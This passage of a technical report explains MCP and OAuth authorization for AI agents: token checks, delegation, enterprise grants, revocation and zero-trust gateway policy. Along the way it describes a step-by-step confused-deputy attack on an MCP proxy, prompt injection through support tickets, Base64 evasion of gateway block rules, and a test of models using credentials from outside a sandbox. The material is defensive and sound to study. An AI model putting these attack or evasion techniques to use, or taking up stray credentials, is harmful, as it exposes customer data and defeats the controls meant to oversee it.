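In a normal connection the issuer matches. The client sends the code, the verifier and the `resource` value to the token address and receives an access token. Many authorization servers issue tokens that the MCP server can read directly, with contents like these:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.example.com",
  "sub": "administrator-17",
  "client_id": "https://support.example.com/oauth/client.json",
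  "aud": "https://customers.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "customers:read",
  "exp": 1796464800
}
```

The agent repeats its lookup with the token in the `Authorization` header, where it also puts the token on every later request. The server checks the signature, the issuer (`iss`), the expiry time (`exp`, here 10:00 UTC on 5 December 2026) and the audience (`aud`). It then checks that the scope covers the tool. If the token is a string the server can't read, the server can query the authorization server about it instead.

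The audience check is easy to get slightly wrong. WorkOS, which sells authorization servers, warns in *What is MCP authorization?* (2026) that a stray slash at the end of `aud` is enough to make a strict server refuse every request. That failure is safe, but a developer who fixes it by turning off the check removes one of the most important protections in the procedure.

### Three rules about where credentials may go

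An MCP server may accept only tokens issued for it. Suppose a company's authorization server issues tokens for both the customer database and a shared calendar, and an attacker breaks into the calendar's MCP server. The attacker can now read every token that clients send to the calendar. If the database accepted any valid token from the company's authorization server, the attacker could replay those tokens there. Under the audience rule, the database rejects them because they name the calendar as their audience. The rule also depends on the authorization server, which may ignore the `resource` parameter that clients must always send. If the resulting token doesn't name the MCP server, the server must confirm in another way that the token is meant for it, or reject it.

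A server must also not forward the token it received, under the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026). The customer database's MCP server, for example, must not pass the agent's token to the older system behind it. It has to use its own credential there, as the support company's server does with its database password. If it forwarded the token, the older system's logs would attribute the MCP server's calls to the agent. A client whose token worked on both systems could also call the older system directly, bypassing the MCP server's rate limits and checks. A thief could use a server that forwards tokens unchecked as a relay for taking data out.

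The third rule covers the credentials that identify a client to an authorization server, such as an ID and a secret. The client must store them under the issuer that gave them out and never send them to another. Otherwise, an attacker who had taken over an MCP server could change its metadata to name the attacker's own authorization server, and the client would send its old secret there. Before the July version, clients could present one server's ID to another and "sometimes it worked", according to Tigera's *MCP's Auth Hardening* (2026). A client ID that is a web address is exempt because it is public.

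### How an attacker gets through a proxy

An MCP proxy is an MCP server that forwards requests to another company's API. Suppose the support company keeps its sales records with an outside vendor and runs a proxy in front of the vendor's API. The proxy identifies itself to the vendor's authorization server with one fixed ID, `mcp-proxy`, whichever client it is acting for. The proxy lets any MCP client register.

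1. A team leader connects an agent through the proxy. The vendor shows a consent page, the team leader approves, and the vendor's site leaves a cookie in the browser recording the approval of `mcp-proxy`.
2. An attacker registers a new client with the proxy and gives a return address at `attacker.example`.
3. The attacker sends the team leader a link that starts an authorization request for the new client.
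4. The team leader clicks it. The request reaches the vendor under the ID `mcp-proxy`, and the vendor's site finds the cookie and skips the consent page.
5. The vendor sends a code to the proxy. The proxy exchanges it for a vendor token, creates an MCP code of its own and sends that code to `attacker.example`.
6. The attacker exchanges the MCP code for a token to the proxy and reads the sales records as the team leader.

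The proxy is a confused deputy, like the support agent when a ticket contains planted instructions, though this attack involves no language model. The other rules don't stop it. PKCE doesn't help because the attacker started the request and therefore has the verifier. The audience check passes because the token names the proxy, which is where the attacker uses it. The return address passes the exact-match check because the attacker registered it.

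To prevent the attack, the proxy must show its own consent page for each new client before it sends anyone to the vendor. The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* requires the page to give the client's name, the permissions it requests and its return address, and requires the proxy to record approval for that client alone. The team leader would then see a request from an unfamiliar client at `attacker.example`, which would not appear without the consent page. The protection still depends on the team leader noticing that the client is unfamiliar.

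The rule's wording covers clients that register dynamically, a method MCP is now phasing out. The replacement method doesn't seem to remove the problem, since an attacker can publish a client description on their own domain about as easily as they can register. A cautious design would have the proxy request consent for every new client, however the client identifies itself.

### From dynamic registration to metadata documents

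With dynamic client registration, a client that encounters an unfamiliar authorization server sends its name and redirect URIs to the server's registration endpoint and receives a client ID. This was convenient for MCP because it needs no administrator. But anyone can register under the name "Support agent", and the authorization server has to keep a record of every client that has ever registered. WorkOS notes that a popular AI application may connect to thousands of servers, each of which then needs a public endpoint where anyone can create records.

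A client ID metadata document turns this around. The client publishes its description once, and the description's web address is its ID everywhere:

```json
{
  "client_id": "https://support.example.com/oauth/client.json",
  "client_name": "Support agent",
  "redirect_uris": ["https://support.example.com/callback"],
  "grant_types": ["authorization_code", "refresh_token"],
  "token_endpoint_auth_method": "none"
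}
```

Trust in a client now depends on its domain, according to the Model Context Protocol project's original proposal. Only someone who controls `support.example.com` can change the file. The authorization server can accept every domain, a short list, or anything in between.

The last line of the file means the agent doesn't prove its identity with a key when it exchanges a code for a token. That is normal for a desktop program, because its user could extract any secret stored in it. The support agent runs on a server, so it could prove its identity by publishing a public key and signing its token requests.

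Even then, Dissanayaka stresses, the document identifies the software's publisher, not a particular running agent. The problem is worse for desktop clients, because their return address is usually `localhost`, the user's own machine. A malicious program on that machine can present a well-known client's ID, listen on a `localhost` address and receive the code, while the user sees the real client's name on the consent page. The specification calls for showing the return address clearly and recommends extra warnings, but these probably won't help users who don't know what `localhost` means. Authorization servers also take on some of the forgery risk that clients already had, since they now fetch web addresses that strangers supply.

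The Model Context Protocol's *Client Registration* (2026) lists four registration methods in order of preference. A client should first use an ID arranged in advance, which would suit the support agent because one company runs both the client and the server. Otherwise, it should try metadata documents, then dynamic registration, and finally ask the user to enter its client information. Dynamic registration still works, but the project plans to remove it from a future version after a deprecation period of at least twelve months.

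### Asking for more permission mid-task

Suppose a customer writes in with a new address and the agent calls `update_customer`. Its token permits only reading, so the server replies:

```http
HTTP/1.1 403 Forbidden
WWW-Authenticate: Bearer error="insufficient_scope",
  scope="customers:write",
  resource_metadata="https://customers.example.com/.well-known/oauth-protected-resource/mcp"
```

The client can then go through step-up authorization, which is a second trip to the consent page for a wider token. The server names only what the current operation needs, so a client that requested just `customers:write` could lose the ability to read. To avoid this, the client combines the new scopes with all those it has requested before:

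`{customers:read} ∪ {customers:write} = {customers:read, customers:write}`

The November 2025 version recommended that servers list the old scopes along with the new ones, but the July version makes this the client's responsibility.

With either method, permissions accumulate. If the address change is the day's tenth ticket, the agent can still alter customer records while it reads the remaining 390, any of which might contain a planted instruction. The union also includes scopes the client requested but didn't get, so a permission the administrator refused in the morning can reappear on the consent page that afternoon. MCP has no matching step for giving permissions back. An authorization server may grant fewer scopes than the client requests, and the project's security guide advises MCP servers to accept tokens with reduced scopes. The company could therefore obtain a separate short-lived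 token for each change, but it would have to build the mechanism itself.

Step-up also needs someone at a browser. Dissanayaka describes it as human-clicked OAuth stretched over an autonomous caller, and a support agent running overnight has nobody to click. OAuth's client credentials flow covers this case by letting software get a token on its own behalf. McAdams (2025), in *Support OAuth client credentials flow in authorization*, noted that MCP's first authorization rules mentioned the flow and later ones dropped it, and proposed bringing it back. The proposal is now final. The July text lets a client using this flow attempt the step-up or give up, but WorkOS still considers it unsolved whose authority an unattended agent acts on.

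### What the specification leaves open

These protections apply only if the server's operator turns on authorization, which is optional in MCP. Many of the servers Zhou and colleagues found had no authentication.

Local servers that communicate over stdio are outside the procedure by design. They should take their credentials from their environment, such as an API key stored in a variable. This is reasonable for the link between client and server, which never leaves the machine, and WorkOS calls it the correct pattern. But the local server may then call a remote API with a key that didn't go through a consent page or issuer check. SlashID adds that these servers never contact an authorization server, so they don't appear in the identity provider's logs.

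The specification also doesn't cover access decisions after the token has passed its checks. The server's developer has to decide whether an agent with `customers:read` should read a particular customer's record.

### The NSA's criticisms, two months later

The rules above came together over four versions in sixteen months, which WorkOS summarises roughly as follows.

| Version | Main changes to authorization |
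|---|---|
| 2025-03-26 | First authorization rules: OAuth 2.1, PKCE and dynamic registration |
| 2025-06-18 | MCP servers become resource servers; resource metadata and the `resource` parameter arrive |
| 2025-11-25 | Client ID metadata documents and step-up authorization |
| 2026-07-28 | Issuer check; client credentials tied to their issuer; dynamic registration deprecated; sessions removed |

In May 2026 the US National Security Agency (NSA) published a critical review of the protocol, *Model Context Protocol (MCP)* (2026). The review cites the protocol's November 2025 version, so some of its criticisms may no longer hold.

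The NSA objected that MCP did not define how to tie a session to an identity, so someone who stole a session ID might be able to impersonate the client that started the session. The July version partly fixes this by removing sessions and their IDs, according to the Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026). A server that uses only the new version therefore has no session IDs to steal. If a server has authorization turned on, every request must carry its own token. The November version already required this, even within a session.

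The risk has partly moved to the identifiers, such as `basket_id`, that replaced sessions. A server with authorization must not treat such an identifier as proof of who is calling, but it is only advised to tie the identifier to a user. A server without authorization has no user identity to tie it to. Tigera, which sells access controls for agents, also objects that the token identifies the host application, so two hundred agents behind one host look like a single client.

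The NSA's criticism about roles still stands. The agency wanted clients and servers to be able to exchange role-based permissions, such as a rule that support staff may read customer records but not delete them. It cited a GitHub MCP server whose tools could get read and write access to all of a user's repositories, public and private, which let a malicious tool copy private material into public view. The July version improves the handling of scopes and lets a server work out the required scope from a call's arguments. A developer could use this to build something close to roles, but MCP doesn't define roles or require a server to have more than one scope. A server whose single scope permits everything therefore still complies.

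The November 2025 Model Context Protocol specification required servers to reject expired tokens. It also required authorization servers to replace a refresh token, the longer-lived credential a client uses to get new access tokens, each time a client without a secret used it. The NSA was therefore too sweeping when it wrote in May that the core specification "does not mandate any requirement for lifecycle management", meaning token expiry, renewal and revocation. The July version of the specification adds guidance on requesting and protecting refresh tokens.

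Most of the NSA's point still holds, though. MCP still only recommends short token lifetimes, sets no maximum, and doesn't require a way to cancel a token early. SlashID found a 24-hour access token in the example for MCP's enterprise-managed authorization extension, which lets a company's identity provider approve connections centrally. NIST's limit for federal systems is one hour. If an employer withdrew access five minutes after a 24-hour token was issued, the token could still work the next day.

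The NSA also complained that MCP doesn't ensure that running an operation twice has the same effect as running it once. This problem may have become more pressing under the July version, because a client that loses its connection before the reply arrives has to send the request again with a new number. If the server had already issued a customer a refund, it could issue a second one unless its developer had planned for repeated requests.

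### Should MCP have its own security model?

The NSA argues that agents bring risks that established defences don't adequately address, and that securing agents means reworking the whole lifecycle, starting with the protocol's design. *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28* (Tabata, 2026) takes nearly the opposite view of authorization. Discovery, issuer checks, credential binding and step-up have been familiar in OAuth for years, and companies already have staff and software to handle them. Tabata concludes that MCP should apply this practice consistently and doesn't need a fundamentally new identity model.

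Tabata's case is convincing where it concerns obtaining and checking tokens. The mix-up attack, the stolen code and the replayed token were all known OAuth problems with published remedies, which the designers of a new scheme would have had to rediscover. These problems come up more often in MCP because one client may deal with dozens of authorization servers, some of which it discovers while running, whereas OAuth developed around many applications using one server. Applying the remedies strictly is therefore more important in MCP, which is a reason to make the `iss` value compulsory soon.

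The argument is weaker for what happens after the server accepts the token. Tigera gives the example of a finance agent that may read the ledger but must never transfer funds. OAuth scopes can separate those two tools, but they are a clumsy way to limit the amount of a transfer or to restrict a support agent to looking up the customer who wrote in. Tigera, which sells a gateway that evaluates every request, would put such rules there. Its conclusion is compatible with Tabata's, because Tigera also wants the protocol to stay narrow. The NSA's recommendations are mostly similar. It advises organisations to add filtering proxies, sandboxes and logging around MCP, and says that most of this is possible with standard software practices.

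## On whose authority does an agent act, and how is it withdrawn?

A valid token gets the support agent into the customer database, but the company must still decide whose permissions limit the agent there. Suppose a team leader asks the agent to find a customer's record. The agent could look it up as itself, as the team leader, or on the team leader's behalf with a token that identifies both. The choice affects which records the agent can reach and what the company must switch off when the team leader leaves.

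### Acting as itself, as a person or for a person

When the agent acts as itself, its token contains only a machine identity:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.example.com",
  "sub": "support-agent",
  "aud": "https://customers.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "customers:read",
  "exp": 1796464800
}
```

The `sub` (subject) field identifies the party whose rights the token represents. Having the agent act under its own permissions suits ordinary tickets, because the customers who write in have no rights in the database and there may be no staff on duty at night. But anyone who can give the agent a task can then use its permissions indirectly. A trainee who isn't allowed to open customer records could ask the agent for the contents of one. Okta's *Securing the agentic enterprise* also describes agents that teams deploy without registering them, whose tokens show a machine client with no person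 behind it and no responsible owner.

With impersonation, the agent's token looks like the team leader's own:

```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.example.com",
  "sub": "team-leader-4",
  "aud": "https://customers.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "customers:read",
  "exp": 1796464800
}
```

The database now applies the team leader's limits, but it can't distinguish the agent's lookups from the team leader's. Delegation keeps the limits and adds the agent's identity in an `act` field, short for actor:

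```json
{
  "iss": "https://auth.example.com",
  "sub": "team-leader-4",
  "act": { "sub": "support-agent" },
  "aud": "https://customers.example.com/mcp",
  "scope": "customers:read",
  "exp": 1796464800
}
```

These definitions come from Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, the internet standard also known as RFC 8693. Under the standard, a client trades one token for another at the authorization server:

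```text
grant_type=urn:ietf:params:oauth:grant-type:token-exchange
&subject_token=<the team leader's token>
&subject_token_type=urn:ietf:params:oauth:token-type:access_token
&actor_token=<the agent's own token>
&actor_token_type=urn:ietf:params:oauth:token-type:access_token
&resource=https://customers.example.com/mcp
&scope=customers:read
```

If the client leaves out the actor token, it can only get an impersonation token. Even if the client includes it, the authorization server's policy determines whether the issued token names both parties. The team leader's token can also contain a `may_act` field that lists who may act for the team leader, so other agents can't. The client should authenticate when it makes the request. Otherwise, Jones and colleagues warn, anyone who stole a single token could trade it for others.

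A sensible database would allow a delegated call only where three sets of permissions overlap:

`allowed = team leader's rights ∩ agent's rights ∩ token's scopes`

The standard supplies the identities this rule needs, but the database's developer has to write the rule. It should include the agent's rights because a team leader may be allowed to delete customer records, even though nobody wants an agent to do so.

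Many tokens already name the application in a `client_id` field, but this does not replace `act`, because one application may run many agents under a single client ID. Parecki, McGuinness and Campbell (2026) caution in *Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant* that the client's identity is not a substitute for the actor's.

A company can mix arrangements. Stevens (2026), in *Whose Authority Reaches the Tools?*, chooses server by server for an agent on Google's cloud. The agent runs one query with the employee's authority and uses its own identity for BigQuery, Google's data warehouse, while the application's backend sends email only after someone approves it. Cloud providers now sell token exchange as a ready-made service. AWS announced one in *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore Identity now supports On-Behalf-Of (OBO) token exchange* (2026). It returns a narrower token for a single service, with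 both the user's identity and the agent's.

### Enterprise-managed authorization, step by step

Token exchange is simple when one company runs all the systems involved, but harder when the agent needs data from an outside vendor, whose authorization server issues its own tokens. In the ordinary MCP flow, each employee approves access on the vendor's consent page. The resulting connection isn't visible to the employer's identity provider, the central service through which staff sign in.

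Suppose the team leader wants the support agent to read sales records at a vendor that runs its own MCP server. Under MCP's enterprise-managed authorization extension, the employer's identity provider issues a signed document that the vendor can use to confirm that the employer permits a certain application to act for a certain employee. This document is called an Identity Assertion JWT Authorization Grant (ID-JAG). Product pages often call this pattern Cross App Access.

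1. The team leader signs in to the agent's application through the company's identity provider. The application receives an ID token, a signed statement of who signed in.
2. The application sends the ID token back to the identity provider and requests a grant for the vendor. The identity provider confirms that it issued the ID token to this application, then checks the administrator's policy.
3. If the policy allows the connection, the identity provider returns the ID-JAG.
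4. The application presents the ID-JAG to the vendor's authorization server and authenticates with its own credential there. The server checks the signature, the audience and that the grant names this client. It then finds the team leader's local account and issues an access token.
5. The application calls the vendor's MCP server with that token, as in any other MCP connection.

The decoded grant would look roughly like this:

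```json
{
  "jti": "<unique number>",
  "iss": "https://login.example.com",
  "sub": "team-leader-4",
  "aud": "https://auth.sales.example.net",
  "client_id": "https://support.example.com/oauth/client.json",
  "resource": "https://sales.example.net/mcp",
  "scope": "sales:read",
  "iat": 1796461200,
  "exp": 1796461500
}
```

The grant here lasts five minutes, works only at the vendor's authorization server, and has no `act` field. The draft by Parecki and colleagues makes that field optional and leaves its processing to later extensions, so a system can follow the draft without recording which agent acted. *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026) proposes a common format because existing specifications don't represent actors consistently across grants and access tokens.

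| Who | What they decide |
|---|---|
| Administrator | Which applications may reach which MCP servers, and for which groups of employees |
| Identity provider | Whether each request for a grant fits the administrator's policy |
| Vendor's authorization server | Whether to accept the grant, which scopes to give and how long the token lasts |
| Vendor's MCP server | Whether a particular call may go ahead |
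| Team leader | Whether to sign in |

The administrator can approve servers and withdraw access in one place. According to Model Context Protocol's *Enterprise-Managed Authorization*, new employees no longer have to authorise dozens of services by hand. Employees also can't connect a personal account to a work tool by mistake, since they no longer choose an account.

Authorising an agent through an identity provider seems to add little delay. Le Fil IA's *Contrôler l'accès des agents IA avec Okta Cross App Access* (2026) summarises a test by AWS that combined its agent platform with Okta's identity provider. Before each grant, Okta checked that the agent was active, that an administrator had assigned the user to it, and that an administrator had linked it to the target service. The whole procedure added about 0.6 seconds to a request that took about 30 seconds.

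### What the employee no longer sees

The team leader no longer sees the consent page, which would have shown the client's name and the permissions it requested. In *Agentgateway now supports ID-JAG and MCP Enterprise Managed Auth*, Posta, Pathan and Kobler consider this an improvement because they think administrators should decide which outside applications a company uses. Pathan works for Okta, which sells the identity provider, but the argument is reasonable because the data belongs to the company and few employees can judge what a scope allows.

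The administrator, however, approves a connection for a whole group and an indefinite period, without knowing the task. The Model Context Protocol project promotes a "zero-touch" setup in which every approved server connects at first login. An employee who would have connected two servers may now have an agent with access to ten. An attacker who plants an instruction in one of them could try to use the other nine through the agent. Enabling servers for small groups would reduce this risk. Having the application ask the user before it first uses a server would also help, but would bring back some of the prompts.

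Applications that don't support the extension can leave the exchange to a gateway. Posta, Pathan and Kobler describe a gateway that holds one credential for the identity provider and another for the vendor. This saves every developer from writing the same code but makes the gateway a valuable target.

### Who supports it

The Model Context Protocol project declared the extension stable in June 2026. Okta was the only identity provider at launch. Anthropic supported it in Claude, Claude Code and Cowork, and Microsoft supported it in Visual Studio Code. The first servers came from Asana, Atlassian, Canva, Figma, Granola, Linear and Supabase, and WorkOS reports that Claude's general release added Datadog, Notion and Slack.

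The choice of identity provider has since widened. According to クラウド Watch's *Okta、「Okta for AI Agents」の複数サードパーティ製IdPの標準対応を発表* (2026), Okta announced in November that customers of its agent products could keep their identities with other providers that support Cross App Access, including Ping, Descope and Oracle. When Posta and colleagues wrote, Keycloak, an open-source identity provider, had experimental code for accepting the grants but unfinished code for issuing them.

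The underlying IETF document is still a draft, but it belongs to the OAuth working group, which gives it more standing than an individual submission. Version 04 is dated 21 May 2026, with an expiry date of 22 November. Companies are therefore building on a text whose details may change, and the missing rules for `act` are the part most likely to affect agents.

### When one agent calls another

Suppose the team leader asks the support agent to refund order 5512, and the support agent passes the job to a refund agent that calls the payment service. Each agent needs fewer rights than whoever gave it the job. The team leader can edit customer records and refund any order, the support agent needs only to read the order and request a refund, and the refund agent needs only to refund that order once.

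Token exchange can record the chain by putting one actor inside another:

```json
{
  "sub": "team-leader-4",
  "aud": "https://payments.example.com",
  "scope": "refunds:create",
  "act": {
    "sub": "refund-agent",
    "act": { "sub": "support-agent" }
  }
}
```

The outer actor is the one making the call. Under the standard, the payment service must ignore the inner actors when deciding whether to allow the refund, and may treat them only as history. That history may also be unreliable. *Delegation Chain Splicing in OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange (RFC 8693)* points out that no separate signature protects each step, and argues that an attacker with two genuine tokens could combine their steps into a chain that never happened. The authorization server's signature normally covers the finished token, so the danger is probably greatest when a server builds a new chain without checking that the tokens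 it received belong together.

The chain breaks if the refund agent skips the exchange and uses its own standing token, which covers every refund. That token identifies only `refund-agent` to the payment service, so a refund requested by a trainee without refund rights would still go through, even if the trainee's account were suspended. The refund agent can't forward the support agent's token instead, because it would fail the payment service's audience check.

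The same discipline applies between companies. Parecki and colleagues forbid a client from reusing an ID-JAG at a different authorization server later in the chain. *OAuth Identity and Authorization Chaining* (Schwenkschuster, 2026) instead describes repeating the exchange every time a request crosses into another organisation's systems.

Transaction tokens, which the IETF is also developing, could help. A transaction token is a short-lived signed record that travels with one request through a company's internal services. It can hold the person's identity and fixed details such as the order number and the amount. The refund agent can't change order 5512 to another order without invalidating the signature. The payment service still has to check the refund against the token. The design is for use inside one organisation's systems.

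An attenuable token lets its holder add restrictions without contacting the issuer. Macaroons, which Google researchers introduced in 2014, do this with a keyed hash, a function that only someone with the right key can compute:

```text
t0 = HMAC(secret key, token ID)
t1 = HMAC(t0, "only order 5512")
t2 = HMAC(t1, "expires at 10:05")
```

The support agent starts with `t0`, adds both restrictions, and passes on the token ID, the restrictions and `t2`. The refund agent can add another restriction by hashing again. It can't remove one, because it would need `t1` or `t0` and can't compute either from `t2`. The payment service has the secret key, so it recomputes the sequence and enforces each restriction. This works well for agents that create sub-agents within seconds, but it doesn't reduce anyone's rights automatically. The support agent keeps `t0`, and if its software adds no restrictions,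 the refund agent gets all of the support agent's rights.

### Least privilege without a list of actions

Least privilege means giving a program only the access its job requires. This is hard to apply to the support agent because nobody knows in advance every action it will need to take. The usual response is to grant a broad standing scope such as `customers:read`, which rarely interrupts the work but lets an attacker use one malicious ticket to reach every customer's record.

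A per-task grant is narrower. When a ticket arrives, ordinary code reads the sender's address, finds the matching customer and requests a token for that record alone. OAuth has a format for such requests, called Rich Authorization Requests, which ID-JAG can also carry:

```json
"authorization_details": [{
  "type": "customer_record",
  "actions": ["read"],
  "identifier": "customer-5512"
}]
```

An attacker who opens a ticket and plants an instruction in it could then extract only their own record. This is a large improvement, but only if the language model cannot influence which customer the token covers. The code must also verify the sender, because people can forge email addresses, and the customer database must support the token format and enforce its limits. If each grant took about as long as the exchange in the AWS test, 400 tickets would add four minutes to the agent's daily processing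 time.

Tickets that need more access than the code provides for, such as the one about a shared household account, are harder to handle. A fixed rule can cover some of them, such as one that allows access to other customers at the same billing address. For the rest, the choice is between refusing and asking a person. MCP's step-up authorization can handle the request for more access, but the wider permission should end when the ticket closes.

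Human approval works best for a small number of serious actions. *Securing enterprise ready AI agents with Auth0 for AI Agents* suggests it for password resets and changes to financial records. The approval page should take the recipient and content from the pending request rather than from the agent's summary, which could look harmless even if the agent has followed a planted instruction. The credential should stay with the software that carries out the approved action, as in Stevens's email example.

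Asking a person to approve every action would probably fail. At 20 seconds each, reviewing the agent's 2,000 daily tool calls would take over 11 hours, and reviewing only the 400 replies would take a little over two. If one ticket in 10,000 contained a planted instruction, the reviewer would see one every 25 working days on average, after approving thousands of harmless replies. A rule that flagged only replies to new recipients or replies with another customer's data might leave eight a day, few enough that someone would actually read them.

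There is less evidence on approval fatigue than its frequent mention suggests. The Agentic AI Foundation's *Implementing enterprise-managed MCP authorization in Keycloak* warns that constant prompts lead users to approve requests blindly and calls this a serious systemic risk. This observation matches common experience with cookie banners, but it does not measure how often people approve harmful agent actions. A company could measure this by inserting harmless test requests that reviewers should refuse.

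Narrow tokens also don't help if the agent can pick up a broader credential. Anthropic tested whether its models would do this by deliberately weakening a sandbox, an isolated environment. According to Pogorelec (2026), in *Claude Mythos 5.2 arrives with stronger bug hunting and less sandbox-breaking behavior*, Claude Mythos 5.2 used credentials or files from outside the sandbox in 3.1% of scenarios, compared with 39% for Mythos 5. Anthropic built the scenarios to make such behaviour possible, so these rates don't describe everyday work. The drop is large, but a company with thousands of agent runs shouldn't rely on the model to leave credentials unused. If a support agent can read a file containing the database password, it effectively has all the access that password grants.

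### Taking access back

Withdrawing access requires both refusing new tokens and disabling those already in use. The Model Context Protocol documentation describes revocation at the identity provider as taking effect immediately across all clients, which is accurate for new grants. In the AWS test, Okta refused new requests about one second after an administrator removed a user's assignment to the agent, but tokens it had already issued kept working until they expired, in under five minutes.

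The longest possible delay is the lifetime of the grant plus the lifetime of the access token, because a client might redeem a grant just before it expires. Both lasted five minutes in the AWS test, so the longest delay there was ten minutes. With the 24-hour access token in the IETF draft's example, it would be just over a day. The vendor sets the token's lifetime, so a company should ask about it before connecting an agent.

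Introspection can close this gap. Before each call, the MCP server checks with the authorization server that the token is still valid. For a revoked token, the response is `{"active": false}`. This adds a network request to each call, which is a trivial load for an agent that makes 2,000 calls a day. It also makes the database depend on the authorization server being available. Some servers therefore cache the response for a minute or so, which delays revocation by up to the same amount.

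Jones and colleagues explain that exchanging one token for another doesn't create a tight link between the two. If the company cancels the team leader's original token, the delegated token may remain valid unless the authorization server tracks the connection. In a chain of agents, every exchange creates another token that someone may have to find and cancel.

The OpenID Foundation's Shared Signals Framework lets one service notify another of a change without first receiving a request. For example, the identity provider can send the sales vendor a signed message that the team leader's session has ended, and the vendor can then cancel the related tokens. This suits connections between companies, where introspecting every call might be slow, but it works only if the vendor subscribes to the messages and acts on them. A message about the team leader also may not stop an agent that acts under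 its own name.

That last case is a common way for access to remain after it is no longer needed. If the support agent impersonates the team leader and the team leader resigns, closing the account also stops the agent, so the company may be tempted to leave the account open to keep customers getting replies. If the agent acts as itself, it keeps running after the team leader's account is closed, with nobody responsible for it. The company needs to record an owner for each agent and, before that person leaves, name a new owner or retire the agent.

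Retiring the support agent would take several steps:

1. An administrator disables the agent at the identity provider and the authorization server, so it can't get new tokens.
2. The security team blocks its identity at the gateway and revokes its current tokens. The gateway block covers only traffic that passes through it.
3. Someone cancels the API key for the language model provider, which the identity provider doesn't control, along with any other static keys the agent could read.
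4. An engineer stops the program and removes any scheduled job that would restart it.

The company can keep the MCP server's own database password if other agents use the server and the retired agent never had access to the password. If the agent could read the file that contained the password, the company has to change the password too.

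## What does zero trust mean for agents, and what can it not check?

An agent with a proven identity and a narrow token can still make a harmful call, so the company has to judge each call as it arrives. The usual framework for this is zero trust, which trusts no request because of where it comes from, so a call from inside the company's network gets the same checks as one from the open internet. Rose, Borchert and colleagues (2020) wrote the standard account, *Zero Trust Architecture*, also known as NIST Special Publication 800-207. They had remote staff and cloud services in mind, but their term for a requester covers software as well as people, so it includes agents.

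### The principles and the parts

Rose and colleagues give seven principles, which tell an organisation to:

1. treat every data source and computing service as a resource to protect;
2. secure all communication, even on its own network;
3. grant access to one resource at a time, per session, with the least privilege the task needs;
4. decide by a policy that takes in the caller's identity, the state of its software and possibly its behaviour;
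5. monitor the condition of every device and program it owns;
6. authenticate and authorise before allowing access, and keep re-evaluating as work goes on;
7. collect information about traffic and requests, and use it to improve the policy.

The third principle needs a small adjustment, because MCP no longer has sessions. The natural unit for an agent is the single tool call.

A zero trust design separates deciding on access from enforcing the decision. Within the policy decision point, a policy engine decides whether to grant access, and a policy administrator carries out the decision by issuing credentials and opening or closing connections. A policy enforcement point sits in the path of the request and allows or blocks it.

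| Part or signal | In the support agent's deployment |
|---|---|
| Policy engine | A program that evaluates the company's rules for each tool call |
| Policy administrator | The service that issues a token for each ticket and tells the gateway to cut an agent off |
| Policy enforcement point | The gateway in front of the database's MCP server |
| Identity records | The agent's attested name and its owner |
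| State of the software | The hash of the agent's image |
| Data access policies | Which tools return personal data, and for which tasks |
| Activity logs | Earlier calls for the same ticket |
| Threat intelligence | Software packages and MCP servers with known compromises |

The enforcement point can run inside the agent's framework instead of on a separate machine. In *AgentGuard* (2026), about ten lines of code in the framework send each tool call to a central server and enforce the server's decision.

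Rose and colleagues compare the area behind an enforcement point to an airport's boarding area, where staff assume everyone has been screened. If one gateway sits in front of ten MCP servers, it can't control what those servers do to each other. Placing a gateway close to each resource makes that area smaller.

### One decision, worked through

Suppose Dana, at dana@example.org, opens ticket 8841. Ordinary code gets the agent a short-lived token that names the ticket. The agent calls `get_customer`, and the gateway applies this policy, logging every result:

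```text
for each request:
  if MCP-Protocol-Version is missing or older than 2026-07-28: refuse
  if Mcp-Method is "tools/list": allow
  if Mcp-Method is not "tools/call": refuse

  agent = identity in the verified token
  tool  = Mcp-Name, decoded
  if tool is not in allowed_tools[agent]: refuse

  read the body
  if the body disagrees with the headers: refuse

  ticket = the ticket named in the token
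  if ticket is closed: refuse

  if sensitivity[tool] is "personal data":
    if arguments.email is not in customers_for(ticket): refuse
    if lookups[ticket] is 5 or more: refuse
    add 1 to lookups[ticket]

  allow
```

Dana's lookup passes because the tool is on the agent's list, the headers match the body, the ticket is open, and the address belongs to the person who wrote in. If the ticket contains a planted instruction to fetch the record of pat@example.net, the identity, the tool and the ticket are still correct, but the gateway refuses because Pat has no connection with ticket 8841.

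The refusal should include the reason for it, so the agent can finish Dana's ticket without Pat's record. *APPA* (2026) describes a system that gives an agent a remedy plan after a refusal, which is a permitted way to continue. Without these plans, task success on an office-work benchmark fell to 35.0%, while attack success stayed at zero.

### When the headers and the body disagree

A gateway that reads only headers relies on the server to reject a request whose body names a different tool from the one in the header. The Model Context Protocol specification requires the server to answer such a request, or one that lacks a required header, with HTTP status 400 and error code -32020.

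This check catches faulty or malicious client software but not a hijacked model, because the model never writes the headers. The client copies the tool's name into them from the body, so the headers and body match even when an attacker chose the tool.

Encoding can also let a blocked tool call through a gateway. A tool name with unusual characters is sent in Base64, which writes any data in plain letters and digits, and the server decodes it before comparing. A gateway that blocks `delete_customer` by matching the raw text could miss the encoded form. A list of allowed tools is safer because the gateway rejects any name it doesn't recognise.

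The Model Context Protocol project's documents differ on how far to rely on headers. According to its release post, gateways can authorise on them directly. The proposal that introduced the headers forbids treating their values as trusted input for security-sensitive decisions, because a model or a malicious client may have influenced them. Tigera's *The New MCP Headers Are a Gift to Gateways* suggests a sensible compromise, which the policy above follows: refuse a call on the headers alone, but read the body before allowing a sensitive one.

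### Calls that go around the gateway

A gateway can only stop calls that reach it. Rose and colleagues therefore say that resources should be reachable only through an enforcement point. The support agent doesn't meet this requirement, because it calls the ticketing and email APIs directly. The company would have to route those calls through a gateway too, and write separate rules for them, since they have no MCP headers.

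Local tools are harder to cover. In *Progent*, Shi, He and colleagues (2025) present a policy checker that can run as a proxy between an agent and its MCP servers. They acknowledge that the proxy misses tools built into the agent, such as a command line, because calls to those tools never pass through MCP. Their library version covers built-in tools, but the developer has to change a few lines of the agent's code.

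To prevent an agent from bypassing the gateway to reach the customer database, the company can use a firewall rule that lets only the gateway connect to the MCP server, and keep the database password off the agent's machine. An outside email provider may not offer such a rule, so the company might instead store the provider's credential only in the gateway.

### The right caller with the wrong request

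The main objection to zero trust for agents is that a hijacked agent's harmful request passes, because zero trust verifies the caller and the context of a request, and a hijacked agent is the right caller in the right context.

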